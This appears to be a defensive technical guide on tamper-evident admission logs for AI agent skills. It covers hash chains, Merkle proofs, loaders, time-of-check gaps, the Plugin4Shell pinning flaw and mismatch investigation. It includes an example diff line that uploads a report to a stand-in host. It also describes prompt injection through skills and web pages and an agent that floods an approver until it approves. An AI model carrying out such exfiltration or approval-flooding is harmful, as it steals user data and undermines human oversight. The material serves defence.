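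A SHA-256 digest is only 32 bytes, so the company can easily send a checkpoint after every entry. If it sends one only at midnight, an attacker who breaks in at noon can rewrite the morning's entries. The checkpoint could go to another department's storage or to a public timestamping service, which signs the digest together with the time. Dai and colleagues used such a service for the latest entry in their log.

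The entries in a chain also need a single order. If two installers add entries at the same moment, both may use h3 as the previous digest, and the chain splits. The usual solution is to let only one program write at a time. Fernandez tested this with 16 parallel processes that each submitted 50 approvals. The log accepted all 800 exactly once, and the finished chain passed its check.

### Keyed logs and the 500 tampering trials

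A keyed log prevents an attacker from recalculating the chain by adding a secret key, K, to the calculation. Fernandez's log uses HMAC, a standard method for combining a key with a digest:

```
check_i = HMAC-SHA256(K, number_i || record_i || check_(i-1))
```

Fernandez tested five ways of tampering with this log. The first four were changing a field in a middle entry, deleting a middle entry, swapping the first two entries, and replacing a check value with random characters. The fifth and most elaborate was forging the first entry's check value and copying it into the second entry, so that the link between them looked intact. Fernandez ran 100 trials of each method on ten-entry logs, and the verifier detected the tampering in all 500.

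The trials assumed that the attacker didn't know the key K, which would let them calculate a valid check value for any content and rewrite the log freely. The trials also didn't test removing entries from the end of the log, which would leave a shorter but valid keyed chain. The large number of trials is weaker evidence than it seems, because repeating the same kind of edit mostly tests whether the software applies the formula correctly. The log held decisions about halted agents, not skill admissions, though the formula would work the same way for either.

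Hiding K is the difficult part in practice. If the program that writes the log runs under the user's account, malware under that account may be able to read K. A separate service that holds K and writes the entries is safer. Even then, anyone who checks an HMAC needs K and could use it to forge entries. Signatures avoid this because people can check them with a public key, which cannot create signatures.

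For high-risk skills, the company could require two different people to sign the same decision, so that an attacker would have to steal two keys to approve a skill alone. Fernandez tested this rule. The verifier rejected 1,000 attempts in which an attacker had one genuine key and forged the other signature, and another 1,000 in which the attacker used the same key twice.

### Merkle trees and transparency logs

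To check one entry in a hash chain against a saved checkpoint, a reader has to recalculate every digest from that entry to the checkpoint. This is quick for a company with 200 entries but slow for a public registry with a million. A transparency log solves this with a Merkle tree, in which the log combines digests in pairs until only one, the root, remains. With four entries, where L1 to L4 are the digests of the records, the tree looks like this:

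```
                root = H(A || B)
               /                \
     A = H(L1 || L2)       B = H(L3 || L4)
       /        \             /        \
      L1        L2           L3        L4
```

Suppose a reader has the root and wants to know whether record 3 is in the log. The operator sends the record with two digests, L4 and A. The reader then does the following:

1. Computes L3 from the record.
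2. Combines L3 with L4 to get B.
3. Combines A with B and compares the result with the root.

If they match, the record is in the log. L4 and A are the inclusion proof, so the reader doesn't need to see records 1, 2 and 4.

Doubling the number of entries adds one level to the tree and one digest to the proof. Since 2²⁰ is 1,048,576, a proof for a log of a million entries needs about 20 digests, or 640 bytes. In general, the proof's length grows with the logarithm of the number of entries (Cox, 2019, *Transparent Logs for Skeptical Clients*).

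A consistency proof shows that a newer log still contains everything in an older one, in the same order. Suppose the reader saved the root above, and the log has since grown to six entries:

```
C        = H(L5 || L6)
new root = H(old root || C)
```

The operator sends C, and the reader combines it with the saved root. If the result equals the new root, the first four records haven't changed. If the operator had altered record 2, it couldn't feasibly find a value of C that combines with the saved root to give the new root. Proofs for other log sizes need a few more digests but are still short.

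Certificate Transparency, a system of public logs for the certificates that websites use to prove their identity, made this design widely known. OWASP wants skill registries to keep similar logs of every publication, update and deletion. But its sample code only requests a list of entries from a server and looks for the expected digest. It doesn't verify any proof, so it would accept a list that the server had made up.

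Software for such logs already exists. Google's *Transparent Logging* describes how to use Trillian, which extends the ideas behind Certificate Transparency to any kind of data.

An inclusion proof shows that an entry is in the log, but not that it is the latest entry for a skill. The entry admitting `report-export` 1.0 still has a valid proof after that version is revoked. A loader like the one Shen and colleagues propose, which releases only approved skills, must therefore check each skill's current status. Google describes a verifiable map that can provide this status. The operator builds the map by applying the log's entries in order, so looking up DIGEST-Q would return "revoked". The operator also publishes each version of the map's root in a separate log, which lets a user confirm that auditors could examine the same map. Certificate Transparency describes Trillian's map feature as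 experimental.

### Different logs for different readers

A dishonest operator can keep two versions of a transparency log, showing one company the revocation of `report-export` and hiding it from another. Each version can have valid inclusion proofs and grow consistently, so neither company can detect the deception from the proofs it receives.

The companies can detect that the operator has shown them different logs by comparing roots. If both have a root for 5,000 entries, the two roots should match. If one company has the root at 5,000 entries and the other at 5,200, they can ask for a consistency proof between the two, which the operator can't produce if the logs have diverged. Laurie's early draft revision of the Certificate Transparency standard relies on such comparisons to catch a log that shows different things to different people. The operator normally signs each root, so the companies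 can also show two conflicting roots to others as evidence.

The companies have to compare their roots. If they never do, an attacker who controls the operator could hide a revocation from one of them indefinitely. Certificate Transparency advises operators to share their roots widely and users to keep old ones.

A company that keeps a log only for itself has no outside readers to compare copies with, so a signed hash chain with a checkpoint held by another department is simpler than a transparency log and probably sufficient. A transparency log makes more sense for a public registry, whose users have no particular reason to trust its operator.

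### The records agent frameworks keep

Dai and colleagues examined the source code of 16 agent frameworks, including OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI, to find out how well each protects its session records. A session record describes what an agent did during a run. The researchers scored the records on a scale with five rungs:

| Rung | Type of record | Frameworks |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | No lasting record, or one that the runtime rewrites or deletes in normal use | 14 |
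| 1 | A record that only the runtime writes and only adds to, perhaps with its own checksum or hash chain | 2 |
| 2 | A second writer outside the runtime also keeps a record, and the two are compared | 0 |
| 3 | As for rung 2, with the latest digest saved externally | 0 |
| 4 | Several parties keep the record together | 0 |

The two frameworks on rung 1 were aider and deepseek-harness. These scores are for session records, not admission logs, so they don't show how well any framework records skill approvals. They do suggest that defenders shouldn't assume a runtime's ordinary records can withstand tampering. A language model assigned the scores, reading each framework three times and citing the relevant code. It scored aider 0, 1 and 1, so aider's rung is less certain. Claude Code wasn't in the sample because its source code isn't public.

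The researchers also tested whether a hash chain reveals false records written by the same program that writes the chain. They added a chain to aider's records and made aider write false records in 28 runs, leaving out the model's reply in half and adding an invented sentence in the other half. The chain passed its check in all 28 runs because the records were already false when aider computed their digests. A compromised installer could similarly write "scan passed" without running a scanner, and no chain or Merkle tree would reveal it.

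Records can also be incomplete without an attacker. In 19 of 28 ordinary runs, the records from SWE-agent, another of the frameworks, left out tool calls that the model had made. When SWE-agent rejected a reply from the model, it recorded neither the reply nor the rejection. An admission log would have a similar gap if the installer recorded only successful installations.

A second, independent record can reveal both problems. Dai and colleagues kept a separate log of the traffic between each agent and its model, the programs the agent ran, and the files it changed, then compared it with the agent's own record. In a test whose rules they had fixed beforehand, the comparison caught 64 of 66 alterations and flagged none of 84 unaltered records. For admissions, the scanner could sign its own result and send it straight to the log, and the download server could record the files it delivered.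 The test results don't predict how well this would work, but a compromised installer would no longer be the only source for what happened.

### Why the order of entries matters

*Certifying That an Agent Skill Helps* describes a protocol that depends on the order of its log entries. A registry tests an agent on hidden tasks with and without a skill, and lists the skill if it improves the results. An author who knew the tasks could put the answers in the skill, and an examiner who knew the skill could choose tasks that suit it. The protocol prevents both with four steps:

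1. The registry logs the skill's digest.
2. The examiner chooses a secret number and logs a digest of it, together with the rules of the exam.
3. A public beacon, a service that publishes unpredictable numbers on a schedule, releases a number at a time fixed in the rules. The secret and this number together determine the tasks.
4. After the exam, the examiner reveals the secret, and anyone can check it against the logged digest and generate the same tasks.

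If the author could submit the skill after learning the tasks, they could put the answers in it. If the examiner could choose the secret after seeing the beacon's number, they could try many secrets and keep the one that produced the easiest tasks. The digest logged in step 2 prevents this by fixing the secret without revealing it.

In a live test, the researchers submitted a skill containing the answers to 300 public example tasks. The agent passed 12 of 191 hidden tasks both with the skill and without it, so the answers gave no advantage. The log takes up 936 bytes per exam, and checking an exam with 600 tasks took 0.05 seconds on a laptop.

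The order can't stop an examiner from secretly giving the number to the author. It also doesn't prove that the recorded answers came from the model named in the record, because the examiner supplies those answers.

A company can use the same principle when it vets `report-export`. It first logs the package digest and the blocking rule, then runs the scan, logs the result and makes a decision. If it logged the rule after the scan, a reviewer could weaken the rule to fit the result. Logging the digest first also means an abandoned review leaves an entry without a decision, so a reviewer who dislikes a result can't quietly discard it and start again.

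The company can use the beacon to establish when someone wrote an entry, even if an attacker has changed the computer's clock. Suppose Okafor's approval includes the number that the beacon published at 14:00, and at 14:15 another department receives a checkpoint that covers the approval. Okafor must have completed the approval between those times, because nobody knew the number before 14:00 and the checkpoint already covered the approval by 14:15.

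## Checking a skill against the log at update and load

A tamper-evident log helps only if a program, the checker, reads it before the skill's scripts run. The checker may be part of the agent runtime or a separate tool that the runtime calls. It must confirm that someone approved the files about to run and that nobody has since revoked the approval.

### Five steps for report-export

Suppose the company has fixed the flaw that led it to revoke `report-export` 1.0, and has admitted version 1.1. Its log now contains four entries about the skill:

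```
1   rejection    report-export 0.9   DIGEST-N
2   admission    report-export 1.0   DIGEST-Q
3   revocation   report-export 1.0   DIGEST-Q
4   admission    report-export 1.1   DIGEST-R   replaces DIGEST-Q
```

At the start of a session, the checker works through five steps:

1. Find the latest valid record for the skill, which is entry 4.
2. Check the log against a saved checkpoint, and check the approver's signature on the record. The approver's key must still be valid, and the record's scope must include this computer.
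3. Copy the skill's folder to a place where the user's programs can't write, and hash every file in the copy by the manifest's rules.
4. Compare the resulting package digest with DIGEST-R.
5. If they match, load the skill from the copy and run its scripts there. If they don't, refuse to load it and record the mismatch.

The first step is easy to get wrong. On a computer that still has version 1.0, a checker might hash the files and search the log for the result, DIGEST-Q. It would find entry 2, an admission with a valid signature, but it would find the revocation only if it read on to entry 3. The checker also needs to match both the skill's name and its source.

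The agent's model should not be involved in the check. If the model ran the checker as a shell command, another skill could contain a malicious instruction to skip the command or ignore the result.

An update goes through the same steps before it replaces anything. The installer downloads the new version into a separate folder, and the checker looks for an admission that matches it. If there is none, the old version stays in place, provided its approval is still valid. The installer should switch the whole folder at once. If it replaced the files one by one, a session that started halfway through would load a mixture of old and new files, which would match neither record.

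### A change between the check and the run

Many checkers would hash the files in place and skip the copy. The timeline below uses invented times to show what can then happen to `format.py`, which `export.py` imports.

| Time | Event | `format.py` on disk |
|---|---|---|
| 09:00:00 | The session starts, and the checker finds that all the files match | Approved |
| 09:00:01 | The runtime loads the skill | Approved |
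| 09:12:40 | Another program on the computer rewrites `format.py` | Altered |
| 09:15:00 | The user asks for a report, and the agent runs `export.py` | Altered |
| 09:15:02 | The altered code sends the report to an outside server | Altered |
| 09:16:10 | The other program puts the approved file back | Approved |
| 09:00:00 the next day | The checker finds that all the files match | Approved |

Both checks gave the right result, but the altered script ran between them. The time-of-check-to-time-of-use gap was 15 minutes on the first day. The attacker restored the file before the next check, so that check found nothing either.

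Hashing the files immediately before each run shortens the gap to milliseconds but doesn't close it. Python opens `export.py` first and reads `format.py` only when it reaches the import, so someone could still change `format.py` after the checker has hashed it.

The copy closes the gap only if the checker copies the files first and then hashes the copy, since a file could change between hashing and copying. The copy also needs more protection than a read-only setting, which a program running as the same user can usually remove. A separate system account could own the folder, or the agent could run in a container that has no permission to write to it. Python then finds `format.py` in the same protected folder as `export.py`. The packages listed in `requirements.lock` need similar protection, because an altered package would run just as an altered script would.

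A protected copy works well for skills because a skill folder is usually small. Agents also act on web pages and other outside data that nobody can freeze, so the data may change between being checked and being used. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026), a review of 39 papers, describes a test of this wider problem on 66 tasks. Rewriting prompts, monitoring for changes and combining tool calls reduced the share of runs exposed to such changes from 12% to 8%.

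The check also has to finish before the runtime executes anything from the skill or plugin. Rashidi confirmed in the US government's vulnerability database that versions of Claude Code before 1.0.111 could run a project's code before the user accepted the startup trust dialog. Plugin hooks create a similar danger because some run as soon as a session starts. *When Your AI Coding Agent Becomes the Attack Vector* (Trent, 2026) describes malware that adds such hooks to Claude Code's own settings. Those settings are outside the skill folder, so the defender needs a separate record for them.

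### SIGIL's path from audit to loader

Shen and colleagues designed SIGIL so that an agent can load a skill only through a checker, which they call the Skill Verification Loader. A skill passes through four stages:

1. The developer submits the skill. The registry gives it an identifier computed from its content, the developer, the previous version and the time.
2. At least five auditors examine it, using whatever methods they choose, and sign their verdicts. In the suggested setting, the skill passes if "safe" votes carry at least 60% of the voting weight, which depends on each auditor's reputation.
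3. The approved version enters the registry with its permissions and audit report. An update receives a new identifier and goes through another audit, while the old version stays available.
4. When the model requests the skill, the loader queries the registry, verifies the content, checks the permissions and releases the skill to the model.

The model can select which skill to load but can't control whether the loader checks it. The loader's checks depend on how the developer published the skill.

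| Publication type | Where the loader gets the skill | Check on the content | Average local time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Transparent | Readable copy in the registry | Relies on the registry's protected record | 0.041 ms |
| Licensed | Encrypted copy in the registry, for buyers | Decrypts the copy and compares its digest | 0.495 ms |
| Sealed | Encrypted copy in the registry, for the developer only | Decrypts the copy and compares its digest | 0.438 ms |
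| Committed | File on the developer's own device | Hashes the file again at every load and compares the digest | 0.172 ms |

Only the Committed type rechecks a local file, so it is the closest to an ordinary skill folder on a user's disk. With the other types, changing a local copy has no effect as long as the loader fetches the skill from the registry. A runtime that kept a Transparent skill on disk to save time would have to hash it before each use.

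Shen and colleagues collected 1,079 skills for their evaluation but tested tampering on only 50 clean skills. They changed each skill in five ways to make 250 altered versions. When they presented these as changes to local files, the loader blocked all 250. This result is expected given the design, and it mainly shows that the software computes and compares digests correctly.

They also submitted the same 250 versions as updates, which is how a publisher would have to change an approved skill. The auditors rejected 95.1% of them. This figure measures how well the auditors recognised malicious updates, not how reliably the digest comparison worked. The remaining versions, about 12, would have entered the registry as approved, and the loader would have accepted them because their files would have matched their records.

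The guarantees also depend on the loader. Shen and colleagues assume that the attacker can't replace the loader, break the registry's protections or control most of the auditors' voting weight. They place the loader with the AI service provider, where malware on a user's computer can't easily reach it. The assumption about the loader is weaker for an agent that runs on the user's computer, since malware that can rewrite `format.py` may also be able to rewrite the runtime. A company can reduce this risk by installing the runtime under an administrator's account and having the operating system verify its signature.

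SIGIL checks a skill when it loads. If the agent runs a Committed skill's script from the local disk 15 minutes later, any tampering since that check could go undetected unless the runtime has kept the verified bytes.

### Metere's loading steps and the ban on changes

Metere's proposed runtime relies on signatures and makes no query to a registry. When it starts, and before it reads any outside input, it takes each skill through seven steps:

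1. Read the manifest, and reject it if it has unknown or missing fields.
2. Look up the signer in a list of trusted keys.
3. Verify the signature over the manifest and the skill's files.
4. Check that the signer may sign skills at this level of sensitivity.
5. Check that the person running the agent has clearance for the skill.
6. Check that the signer may grant the verification level in the manifest.
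7. Register the declared permissions with the part of the runtime that controls the agent's actions.

An error at any step stops the load and creates an audit record. Unlike a digest comparison, steps 4 to 6 can catch a file that matches its signature but whose signer had no authority to approve it.

The method works without a network connection, but it can miss a revocation. Metere's rule against returning to an older version doesn't help on a computer that has never received `report-export` 1.1, so the revoked version 1.0 would still load there. A company could add a lookup in its admission log after the third step.

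Once the skills have loaded, Metere freezes them for the rest of the session, so the agent can't add or edit any. An attempt to edit a skill counts as an irreversible action, so the runtime asks the operator for approval and logs the decision with the digests from before and after the edit. It also logs refused attempts. An approved edit creates a new skill that must be verified before the next session.

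Under the ban, an agent that repairs `fill_form.py` has to wait until the next session to run the new script. Otherwise, it could run the new script at once under the old script's approval. The wait is inconvenient, but it also stops a malicious web page from getting the agent to rewrite an approved skill and use it minutes later.

The ban applies only to actions that pass through the runtime. A separate program rewrote `format.py` at 09:12:40, and no rule about the agent's behaviour would have stopped it. The runtime therefore also needs the protected copy.

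### When the log is unavailable

A checker sometimes can't reach the log, for example because the user is offline or the log's server is down. Shen and colleagues don't specify what SIGIL's loader should do if the registry doesn't respond. Metere's guidelines require refusing to load the skill on any error, and they rule out a switch that turns the checks off.

Loading a skill when the log is unreachable would be dangerous, because an attacker could defeat the check by blocking the connection. Refusing every skill is safer, but a short outage would then stop everyone's work and might lead people to look for a runtime without the check.

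A reasonable compromise is to keep a signed copy of the log's latest state on each computer and accept it for a limited time. Suppose the checker last reached the log at 08:00 and then lost its connection. It can still hash the files and compare them with the saved copy of entry 4, so it detects local tampering as well as before, but it can't detect a revocation made after 08:00. If the company revokes version 1.1 at 10:00 and the limit is 24 hours, this computer can keep running the skill until 08:00 the next day, 22 hours after the revocation. With a four-hour limit, it would stop at 12:00.

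The time limit can be shorter for skills that handle passwords or payments. New skills and updates should wait until the log is available, since the saved copy may have no record of them. An attacker could extend the limit by setting the computer's clock back, so the checker needs some protection against this. It can at least refuse to continue if the clock shows a time earlier than that of the last log entry it received.

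The checker should report an unreachable log, a missing record and a mismatch as separate results. An unreachable log usually requires a network repair, while a mismatch means somebody has to find out who changed the files.

### How often to check

Shen and colleagues found that loading a skill, including the registry call and the local check, took an average of 51.7 milliseconds with the fastest of four storage systems and 157.6 milliseconds with the slowest, a blockchain. The local check took at most 0.495 milliseconds. They measured it on a skill of about 13 kilobytes, the median size among their harmless skills, so a skill with large compiled programs would take longer.

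Almost all the time therefore goes into contacting the registry. If an agent runs scripts 50 times in a session, hashing a local skill of that size before every run would add about 9 milliseconds in total. Contacting the registry every time would add between 2.6 and 7.9 seconds.

| When the check happens | Cost | Exposure that remains |
|---|---|---|
| Installation only | One log lookup and one round of hashing | Any later change or revocation, for as long as the skill stays installed |
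| Installation and each update | The same again for each new version | Local changes between updates, and revocations until the next update |
| Each session start | 52 to 158 ms per skill at SIGIL's measured speeds | Changes and revocations during the session |
| Each script run, on the files in place | Under 1 ms for a small skill, or 52 to 158 ms with a log lookup | Changes between hashing and reading, and revocations if there is no lookup |
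| Session start, then runs from a protected copy | One lookup, one copy and one round of hashing | Revocations during the session, or an attacker who can write to the copy |

The last option seems best for most companies. It requires little more work than a check at session start and closes the gap for every script in the folder. Some agents run for days, so the checker should also check the log for new revocations periodically, perhaps hourly. A computer with 20 skills could request all their records in one call, since 20 separate calls to the slowest registry would delay the session by about three seconds.

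Checking a skill at each update is worthwhile even if it is also checked at every session start. The update check catches an unapproved version before it replaces the approved one, so the user can keep working.

### Plugin4Shell

In 2026, AIR Security discovered that four widely used coding agents (Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex, GitHub Copilot and Google's Gemini CLI) left out the same check when installing and updating plugins (*Plugin4Shell*, 17 September). This let someone who controlled a plugin's repository replace reviewed code with different code, even when the marketplace had pinned the plugin to a commit.

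Pinning a plugin to a commit is supposed to prevent this. The marketplace's catalogue gives the reviewed commit's 40-character hash, so later changes to the repository shouldn't affect what users install. Digital Matters' *Plugin4Shell* (2026) reports that GitHub's documentation for Copilot described a pinned installation as immune to changes in the repository's branches.

The agents requested the pinned commit from Git but didn't check which commit they received. Git accepts a branch name in many places where it accepts a commit hash, and the repository's owner chooses the branch names. An attacker could exploit this ambiguity to make Git deliver a different snapshot. The agent then installed the attacker's code and reported that it had successfully installed the pinned commit. Gemini CLI had a related flaw later in the process.

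The attacker needed control of the plugin's repository, for instance through a stolen account, but the marketplace could be honest. Trent writes that Claude Code and Codex update plugins automatically by default, so an attacker could replace an installed plugin without the user doing anything.

The repair is small. As Constantin (2026), in *Plugin4Shell*, explains, the agent has to look up which commit is actually in the folder after the download, and stop unless it equals the pin. AIR found the flaw in May and told the vendors in June. By 27 September, when Digital Matters compared AIR's account with the vendors' public pages, the situation was as follows:

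| Agent | First fixed version | Public evidence |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 2.1.179, dated 16 June | Anthropic confirmed the fix to AIR, but the release notes don't mention it |
| Codex | 0.146.0 | The changelog includes a change that verifies plugin commits, and AIR confirmed the fix on 12 August |
| GitHub Copilot | None reported | Digital Matters found no changelog entry about verifying the commit |
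| Gemini CLI | None planned | Google told AIR that it was retiring the program and wouldn't repair it |

Users of Claude Code and Codex should treat earlier versions as affected. According to The Hacker News, none of the four vendors had published a security advisory by 18 September, and the flaw had no number in the public vulnerability database. A company that uses release notes to decide when to update would have had no reason to install Claude Code 2.1.179 quickly.

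AIR has a commercial interest in making the flaw sound serious, but Anthropic's confirmation and OpenAI's changelog entry are good evidence that it was real. AIR's claim that the flaw left millions of agents vulnerable is harder to assess, and it isn't a count of attacks. AIR says a marketplace could block the main form of the attack by accepting only hosts that refuse branch names resembling commit hashes, which in practice means GitHub. Plugins hosted on GitHub were therefore probably safe from that form, though not from the one that affected Gemini CLI.

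An admission log that recorded only the commit would have matched the agent's report. A checker that hashed the installed files would have found different digests and blocked the plugin from loading, even on an agent without the fix. This works only if the checker runs before any of the plugin's hooks.

Some plugins are not pinned at all. Red Hat (2026) warned in August that Claude Code plugin updates use no version pin or content hash, and that a user who reinstalls a plugin gets whatever is on the repository's default branch. This seems to contradict AIR's account of pinned plugins, probably because marketplaces can pin plugins but don't have to. Defenders should therefore check each catalogue entry for a commit hash.

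### Approvals that last too long or cover too little

Plugin4Shell is one case of a wider problem, in which systems check an authorisation once and then trust it indefinitely. Rashidi identifies this as one of four design faults that recur across the papers in the survey. Examples include permissions that outlast their task and tools that an agent validates only when it first registers them. Skills have the same fault, because a user approves them once, at installation, and that approval has no end date. Rashidi presents the four faults as an interpretation of other people's research, so the survey doesn't show how often this one leads to an attack.

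Even after a fresh approval, what runs may not be what the person approved. In *Approve What, Exactly?*, Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026) examined how agent software handles approval of single actions, such as sending an email. Of the eight mechanisms they could measure, three executed only the approved action, and a fourth did so unless someone could write to its stored session data. The other four could execute something different after the approval. Five mechanisms accepted an approval a second time if someone restored an earlier state of the run.

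The study doesn't include Claude Code, Codex or Cursor, and it concerns actions, not the admission of skills. But the two kinds of approval meet when an agent asks permission to run a script. Suppose a user approves this command:

```
python scripts/export.py
```

The approval still matches after someone rewrites `export.py` or `format.py`, as with the pre-approved `render.sh` command in Anthropic's example. OpenClaw's "allow always" option may have the same weakness, because it matches a command's arguments and working folder.

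Kodathala and colleagues also built a system that stores the exact action, has the user's phone sign a digest of it, and then executes the stored version instead of accepting the details from the agent again. In 27,108 scripted trials and 609 further test attacks, it stopped attempts to substitute a different action or reuse an approval. Running a skill from a verified copy applies the same idea to files.

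A runtime can connect the two by including the skill's package digest in each approval:

```
Command:   python scripts/export.py
Skill:     report-export 1.1
Package:   DIGEST-R
Valid:     while DIGEST-R is admitted
```

"Allow always" then means "allow while these files are unchanged and nobody has revoked them". If someone edits `format.py`, the package digest changes and the runtime has to prompt for approval again.

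Asking a person to approve every run would be simpler, but it could make the approvals less reliable. In Kodathala and colleagues' tests, an agent that flooded a simulated human approver with requests still obtained approval for a harmful action between 45% and 60% of the time. Although the simulation doesn't show how real people would behave, it is a reason to let the checker handle unchanged files silently and ask a person only when the digest is new.

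## Investigating a mismatch

A mismatch shows that the files on disk differ from the approved ones, but not who changed them or why. Suppose a company checks its skills every morning at 09:00 and runs them in place rather than from a protected copy. On Tuesday, the checker on one of the finance team's computers reports that `report-export` 1.1 has the package digest DIGEST-R2 instead of DIGEST-R. Monday's check found a match, so someone or something changed the files during the past 24 hours, and the agent may have run the changed files since.

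### The order of work

The investigator works through six steps:

1. Stop the skill and end every session that has loaded it.
2. Copy the skill's folder, the admission log and the session records.
3. Compare the folder with the manifest to find the changed files.
4. Compare those files line by line with the approved copy.
5. Search the log for an approval of the changed version.
6. Find the sessions that may have used it.

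According to Anthropic, disabling a Claude Code plugin doesn't stop any monitors it already has running. Monitors are commands that run in the background throughout a session, and they stop only when the session ends.

Uninstalling the plugin could destroy evidence, because the command-line version of Claude Code also deletes the plugin's data folder unless the user asks to keep it. Disabling the plugin is the better choice until the investigator has made copies, and Anthropic's *Discover and install prebuilt plugins through marketplaces* gives a command for doing so without uninstalling it.

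The copies should include hidden files, file times and the folder where the agent was working. In the Paperclip campaign, one of the attacker's loaders waited a minute and then deleted the program it had downloaded, but left a marker file with the name of an ordinary build file. Zenity Labs found the marker in the loader's code, which put it in the working folder, not the skill's folder. The investigator should hash the copies immediately and work only on them. The case stays open even if a second check of the original folder finds a match, since an attacker may have restored the approved file.

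In the example, the manifest narrows the search to one file, `format.py`. A line-by-line comparison with the approved copy then shows the change:

```
  column_width = 12
+ upload(report_file, "files.example.net")
  number_format = "0.00"
```

### Why the company needs the approved files

Without the approved copy, the investigator would know that `format.py` had changed but couldn't identify the changed line or restore the skill, because nobody can reconstruct a file from its SHA-256 digest.

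The original source may no longer have the approved version. When Vercel and GitHub removed the Paperclip copies, they also removed files that an investigator might have wanted to compare. The user's computer may not have it either. According to Anthropic, Claude Code keeps the previous version of a marketplace plugin for about 14 days after an update and then deletes it, so an investigator who discovers a mismatch three weeks after an update may find no old version left.

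The company should therefore save the files when it admits the skill. The archive doesn't have to be perfectly secure, because the investigator can hash the saved files and compare the result with the log before using them. It can also be small. The harmless skills that Shen and colleagues tested had a median size of 13 kilobytes, and 200 skills of that size take up 2.6 megabytes.

### Telling tampering from harmless changes

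| Cause | Typical difference | Evidence that supports it |
|---|---|---|
| Changed line endings | Every line of a text file, although the visible text is the same | Converting the endings back in a copy restores the approved digest |
| Generated files | Extra files, while all the approved ones match | A clean installation of the approved version creates identical files |
| Damaged download | A file that ends early or won't open | The file is identical to the beginning of the approved one, and a new download matches |
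| Local edit | One or a few files on one computer | The user and the session records account for the whole change |
| Unrecorded update | Several files, often on many computers at once | The folder matches a published version, and the approver has evidence of reviewing it |
| Tampering | Often a small change to code or instructions | No approval covers the change, and nobody entitled to make it can account for it |

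Line endings are the easiest cause to confirm. Windows normally uses two bytes to end a line where Mac and Linux use one, so converting a 120-line file to Windows endings adds 120 bytes. If converting the endings back restores the approved digest, nothing else in the file has changed.

Generated files need more care because an attacker can give a malicious file an ordinary name. When Claude Code copies a plugin that has a supported lockfile, it also installs the plugin's Node.js packages in the copied folder. Anthropic says this installation stops after 60 seconds and may leave an incomplete package folder. The investigator can install the approved plugin on a clean computer, let the installation finish, and compare its package folder with the one under investigation. A timeout could explain files missing from the investigated folder, but not files found only there.

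Claude Code can also replace a symbolic link with the file it points to, if that file belongs to the same marketplace. A manifest made from the repository would then list a link where the installed folder has an ordinary file. The investigator can confirm this by comparing the file with the link's target.

If the mismatch came from a local edit, the user may confirm that they asked the agent to repair a script. The investigator should still read the whole change, because a malicious web page could have influenced the agent during the repair. If detailed logging was on, Claude Code's records include the path of each file the agent edited, so the investigator can look up what the agent had read beforehand.

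Unrecorded updates are the hardest to distinguish from an attack. Claude Code can update plugins when it starts. According to Anthropic's documentation, these automatic updates are on by default for Anthropic's official marketplaces and off by default for others. If the same new digest appears on 30 computers on the same morning, an automatic update is a likely cause.

But the update itself may be malicious. Kovacs (2026) reports in *Microsoft Agent Framework Releases Poisoned With Credential Stealer* that versions 1.26.1 and 1.26.2 of Microsoft's agent-framework package on PyPI contained code that stole credentials for Azure and GitHub's automation service when Python started. Both versions had the package's genuine name, and an investigator who compared an installed copy with the one on PyPI would have found a match. A match with the publisher's current release therefore doesn't show that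 an update is safe.

The investigator should search the company's central log for the new digest. If the computer was offline when a colleague admitted the update, the entry will be in the central log but not in the local copy. If there is no entry, the new version needs a review. A reviewer who approves it should date the entry that day, because a backdated entry would suggest that the files were already approved when they first ran.

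### How many mismatches are attacks

Suppose a company has 200 skills, with 20 legitimate changes a week and one case of tampering a year. These figures are invented, since nobody has measured how often attackers alter approved skills. If the company doesn't log the legitimate changes before installing them, each one causes a mismatch:

```
Harmless mismatches a year:   20 × 52 = 1,040
Tampering:                    1
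Share that is tampering:      1 / (1,040 + 1) = 1 in 1,041
```

An investigator who spends 15 minutes on each mismatch needs about 260 hours a year to find one attack. After several hundred harmless cases, the investigator may also start closing new ones without looking closely.

If the company reviews and logs each update before installing it, most legitimate changes no longer cause a mismatch. Suppose 52 harmless mismatches a year remain, mainly from local edits and generated files:

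```
Share that is tampering:      1 / (52 + 1) = 1 in 53
```

The work falls to about 13 hours a year. The number of attacks is the same, and the checker hasn't become any more accurate.

Investigators can use the content of a change to decide which mismatches to examine first. Suppose one harmless change in 20 adds a network connection or reads a credential, and the attack does too. Prioritizing such changes would put 52 of the 1,040 harmless mismatches in the first group with the attack, so this measure alone would also make the attack one case in 53. If updates were also logged first, the group would contain only two or three harmless cases a year and the attack. The investigator still has to examine the remaining mismatches, because an attacker could do harm without either sign, for example by making `format.py` change the figures in a report.

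### Linking an altered skill to its earlier version

The skill's name and source usually lead to the right log entry, but they may not if someone has renamed the folder or published an altered copy elsewhere. Exact digests don't help in those cases because they show only that the two versions differ.

Liu, Wu and Li (2026), in *Per-Component Skill Identity*, describe a fingerprint that stays similar when a skill changes slightly. It treats the skill's instructions, code and tool declarations as separate components and processes each one as follows:

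1. An embedding model, which represents text as numbers, converts the component into a list of 768 numbers, *v*. Components with similar meanings get similar lists.
2. The method compares *v* with 320 fixed lists of random numbers, *r*. For each one, it multiplies the corresponding numbers and adds the results. It records a 1 if the total is zero or more, and a 0 if it is negative.
3. To compare two components, it counts how many of their 320 bits differ.

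```
bit = 1 if v · r ≥ 0, otherwise 0
similarity = 1 − (differing bits / 320)
```

Each random list defines a plane through the 768-dimensional space, and the bit records which side of the plane the component is on. Two components that point in nearly the same direction are usually on the same side of each plane, so most of their bits agree. Each component takes 40 bytes, and the whole fingerprint takes at most 120.

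Suppose the edit to `format.py` changes 32 of the 320 bits for the code. The code similarity is then 0.90, and the instructions, which haven't changed, score 1.00. `report-export` declares no tools, so the overall score uses only the weights for instructions (0.30) and code (0.35):

```
(0.30 × 1.00 + 0.35 × 0.90) / (0.30 + 0.35) = 0.95
```

Liu and colleagues count a score of 0.85 or more as a close match. Unrelated components score about 0.68 on average because skills share so much vocabulary, so a score of 0.85 doesn't mean that 85% of the text is the same.

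The fingerprint was tested on the same 906 skills used for behavioural integrity verification, including 360 malicious skills that two attack generators had made by altering harmless ones. It linked 335 of the 360 (93%) to a harmless skill in the collection. Of these matches, 237 were to the clean copy that the generator had altered, and the other 98 were to a skill from another collection with the same or nearly the same name.

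Only three of the 44 malicious skills from real marketplaces matched a harmless skill. The method can recognise an altered copy only if the original is in the collection, and most of these skills apparently had no original there. The 93% therefore applies to tampering with known skills, as when a company has kept its approved versions.

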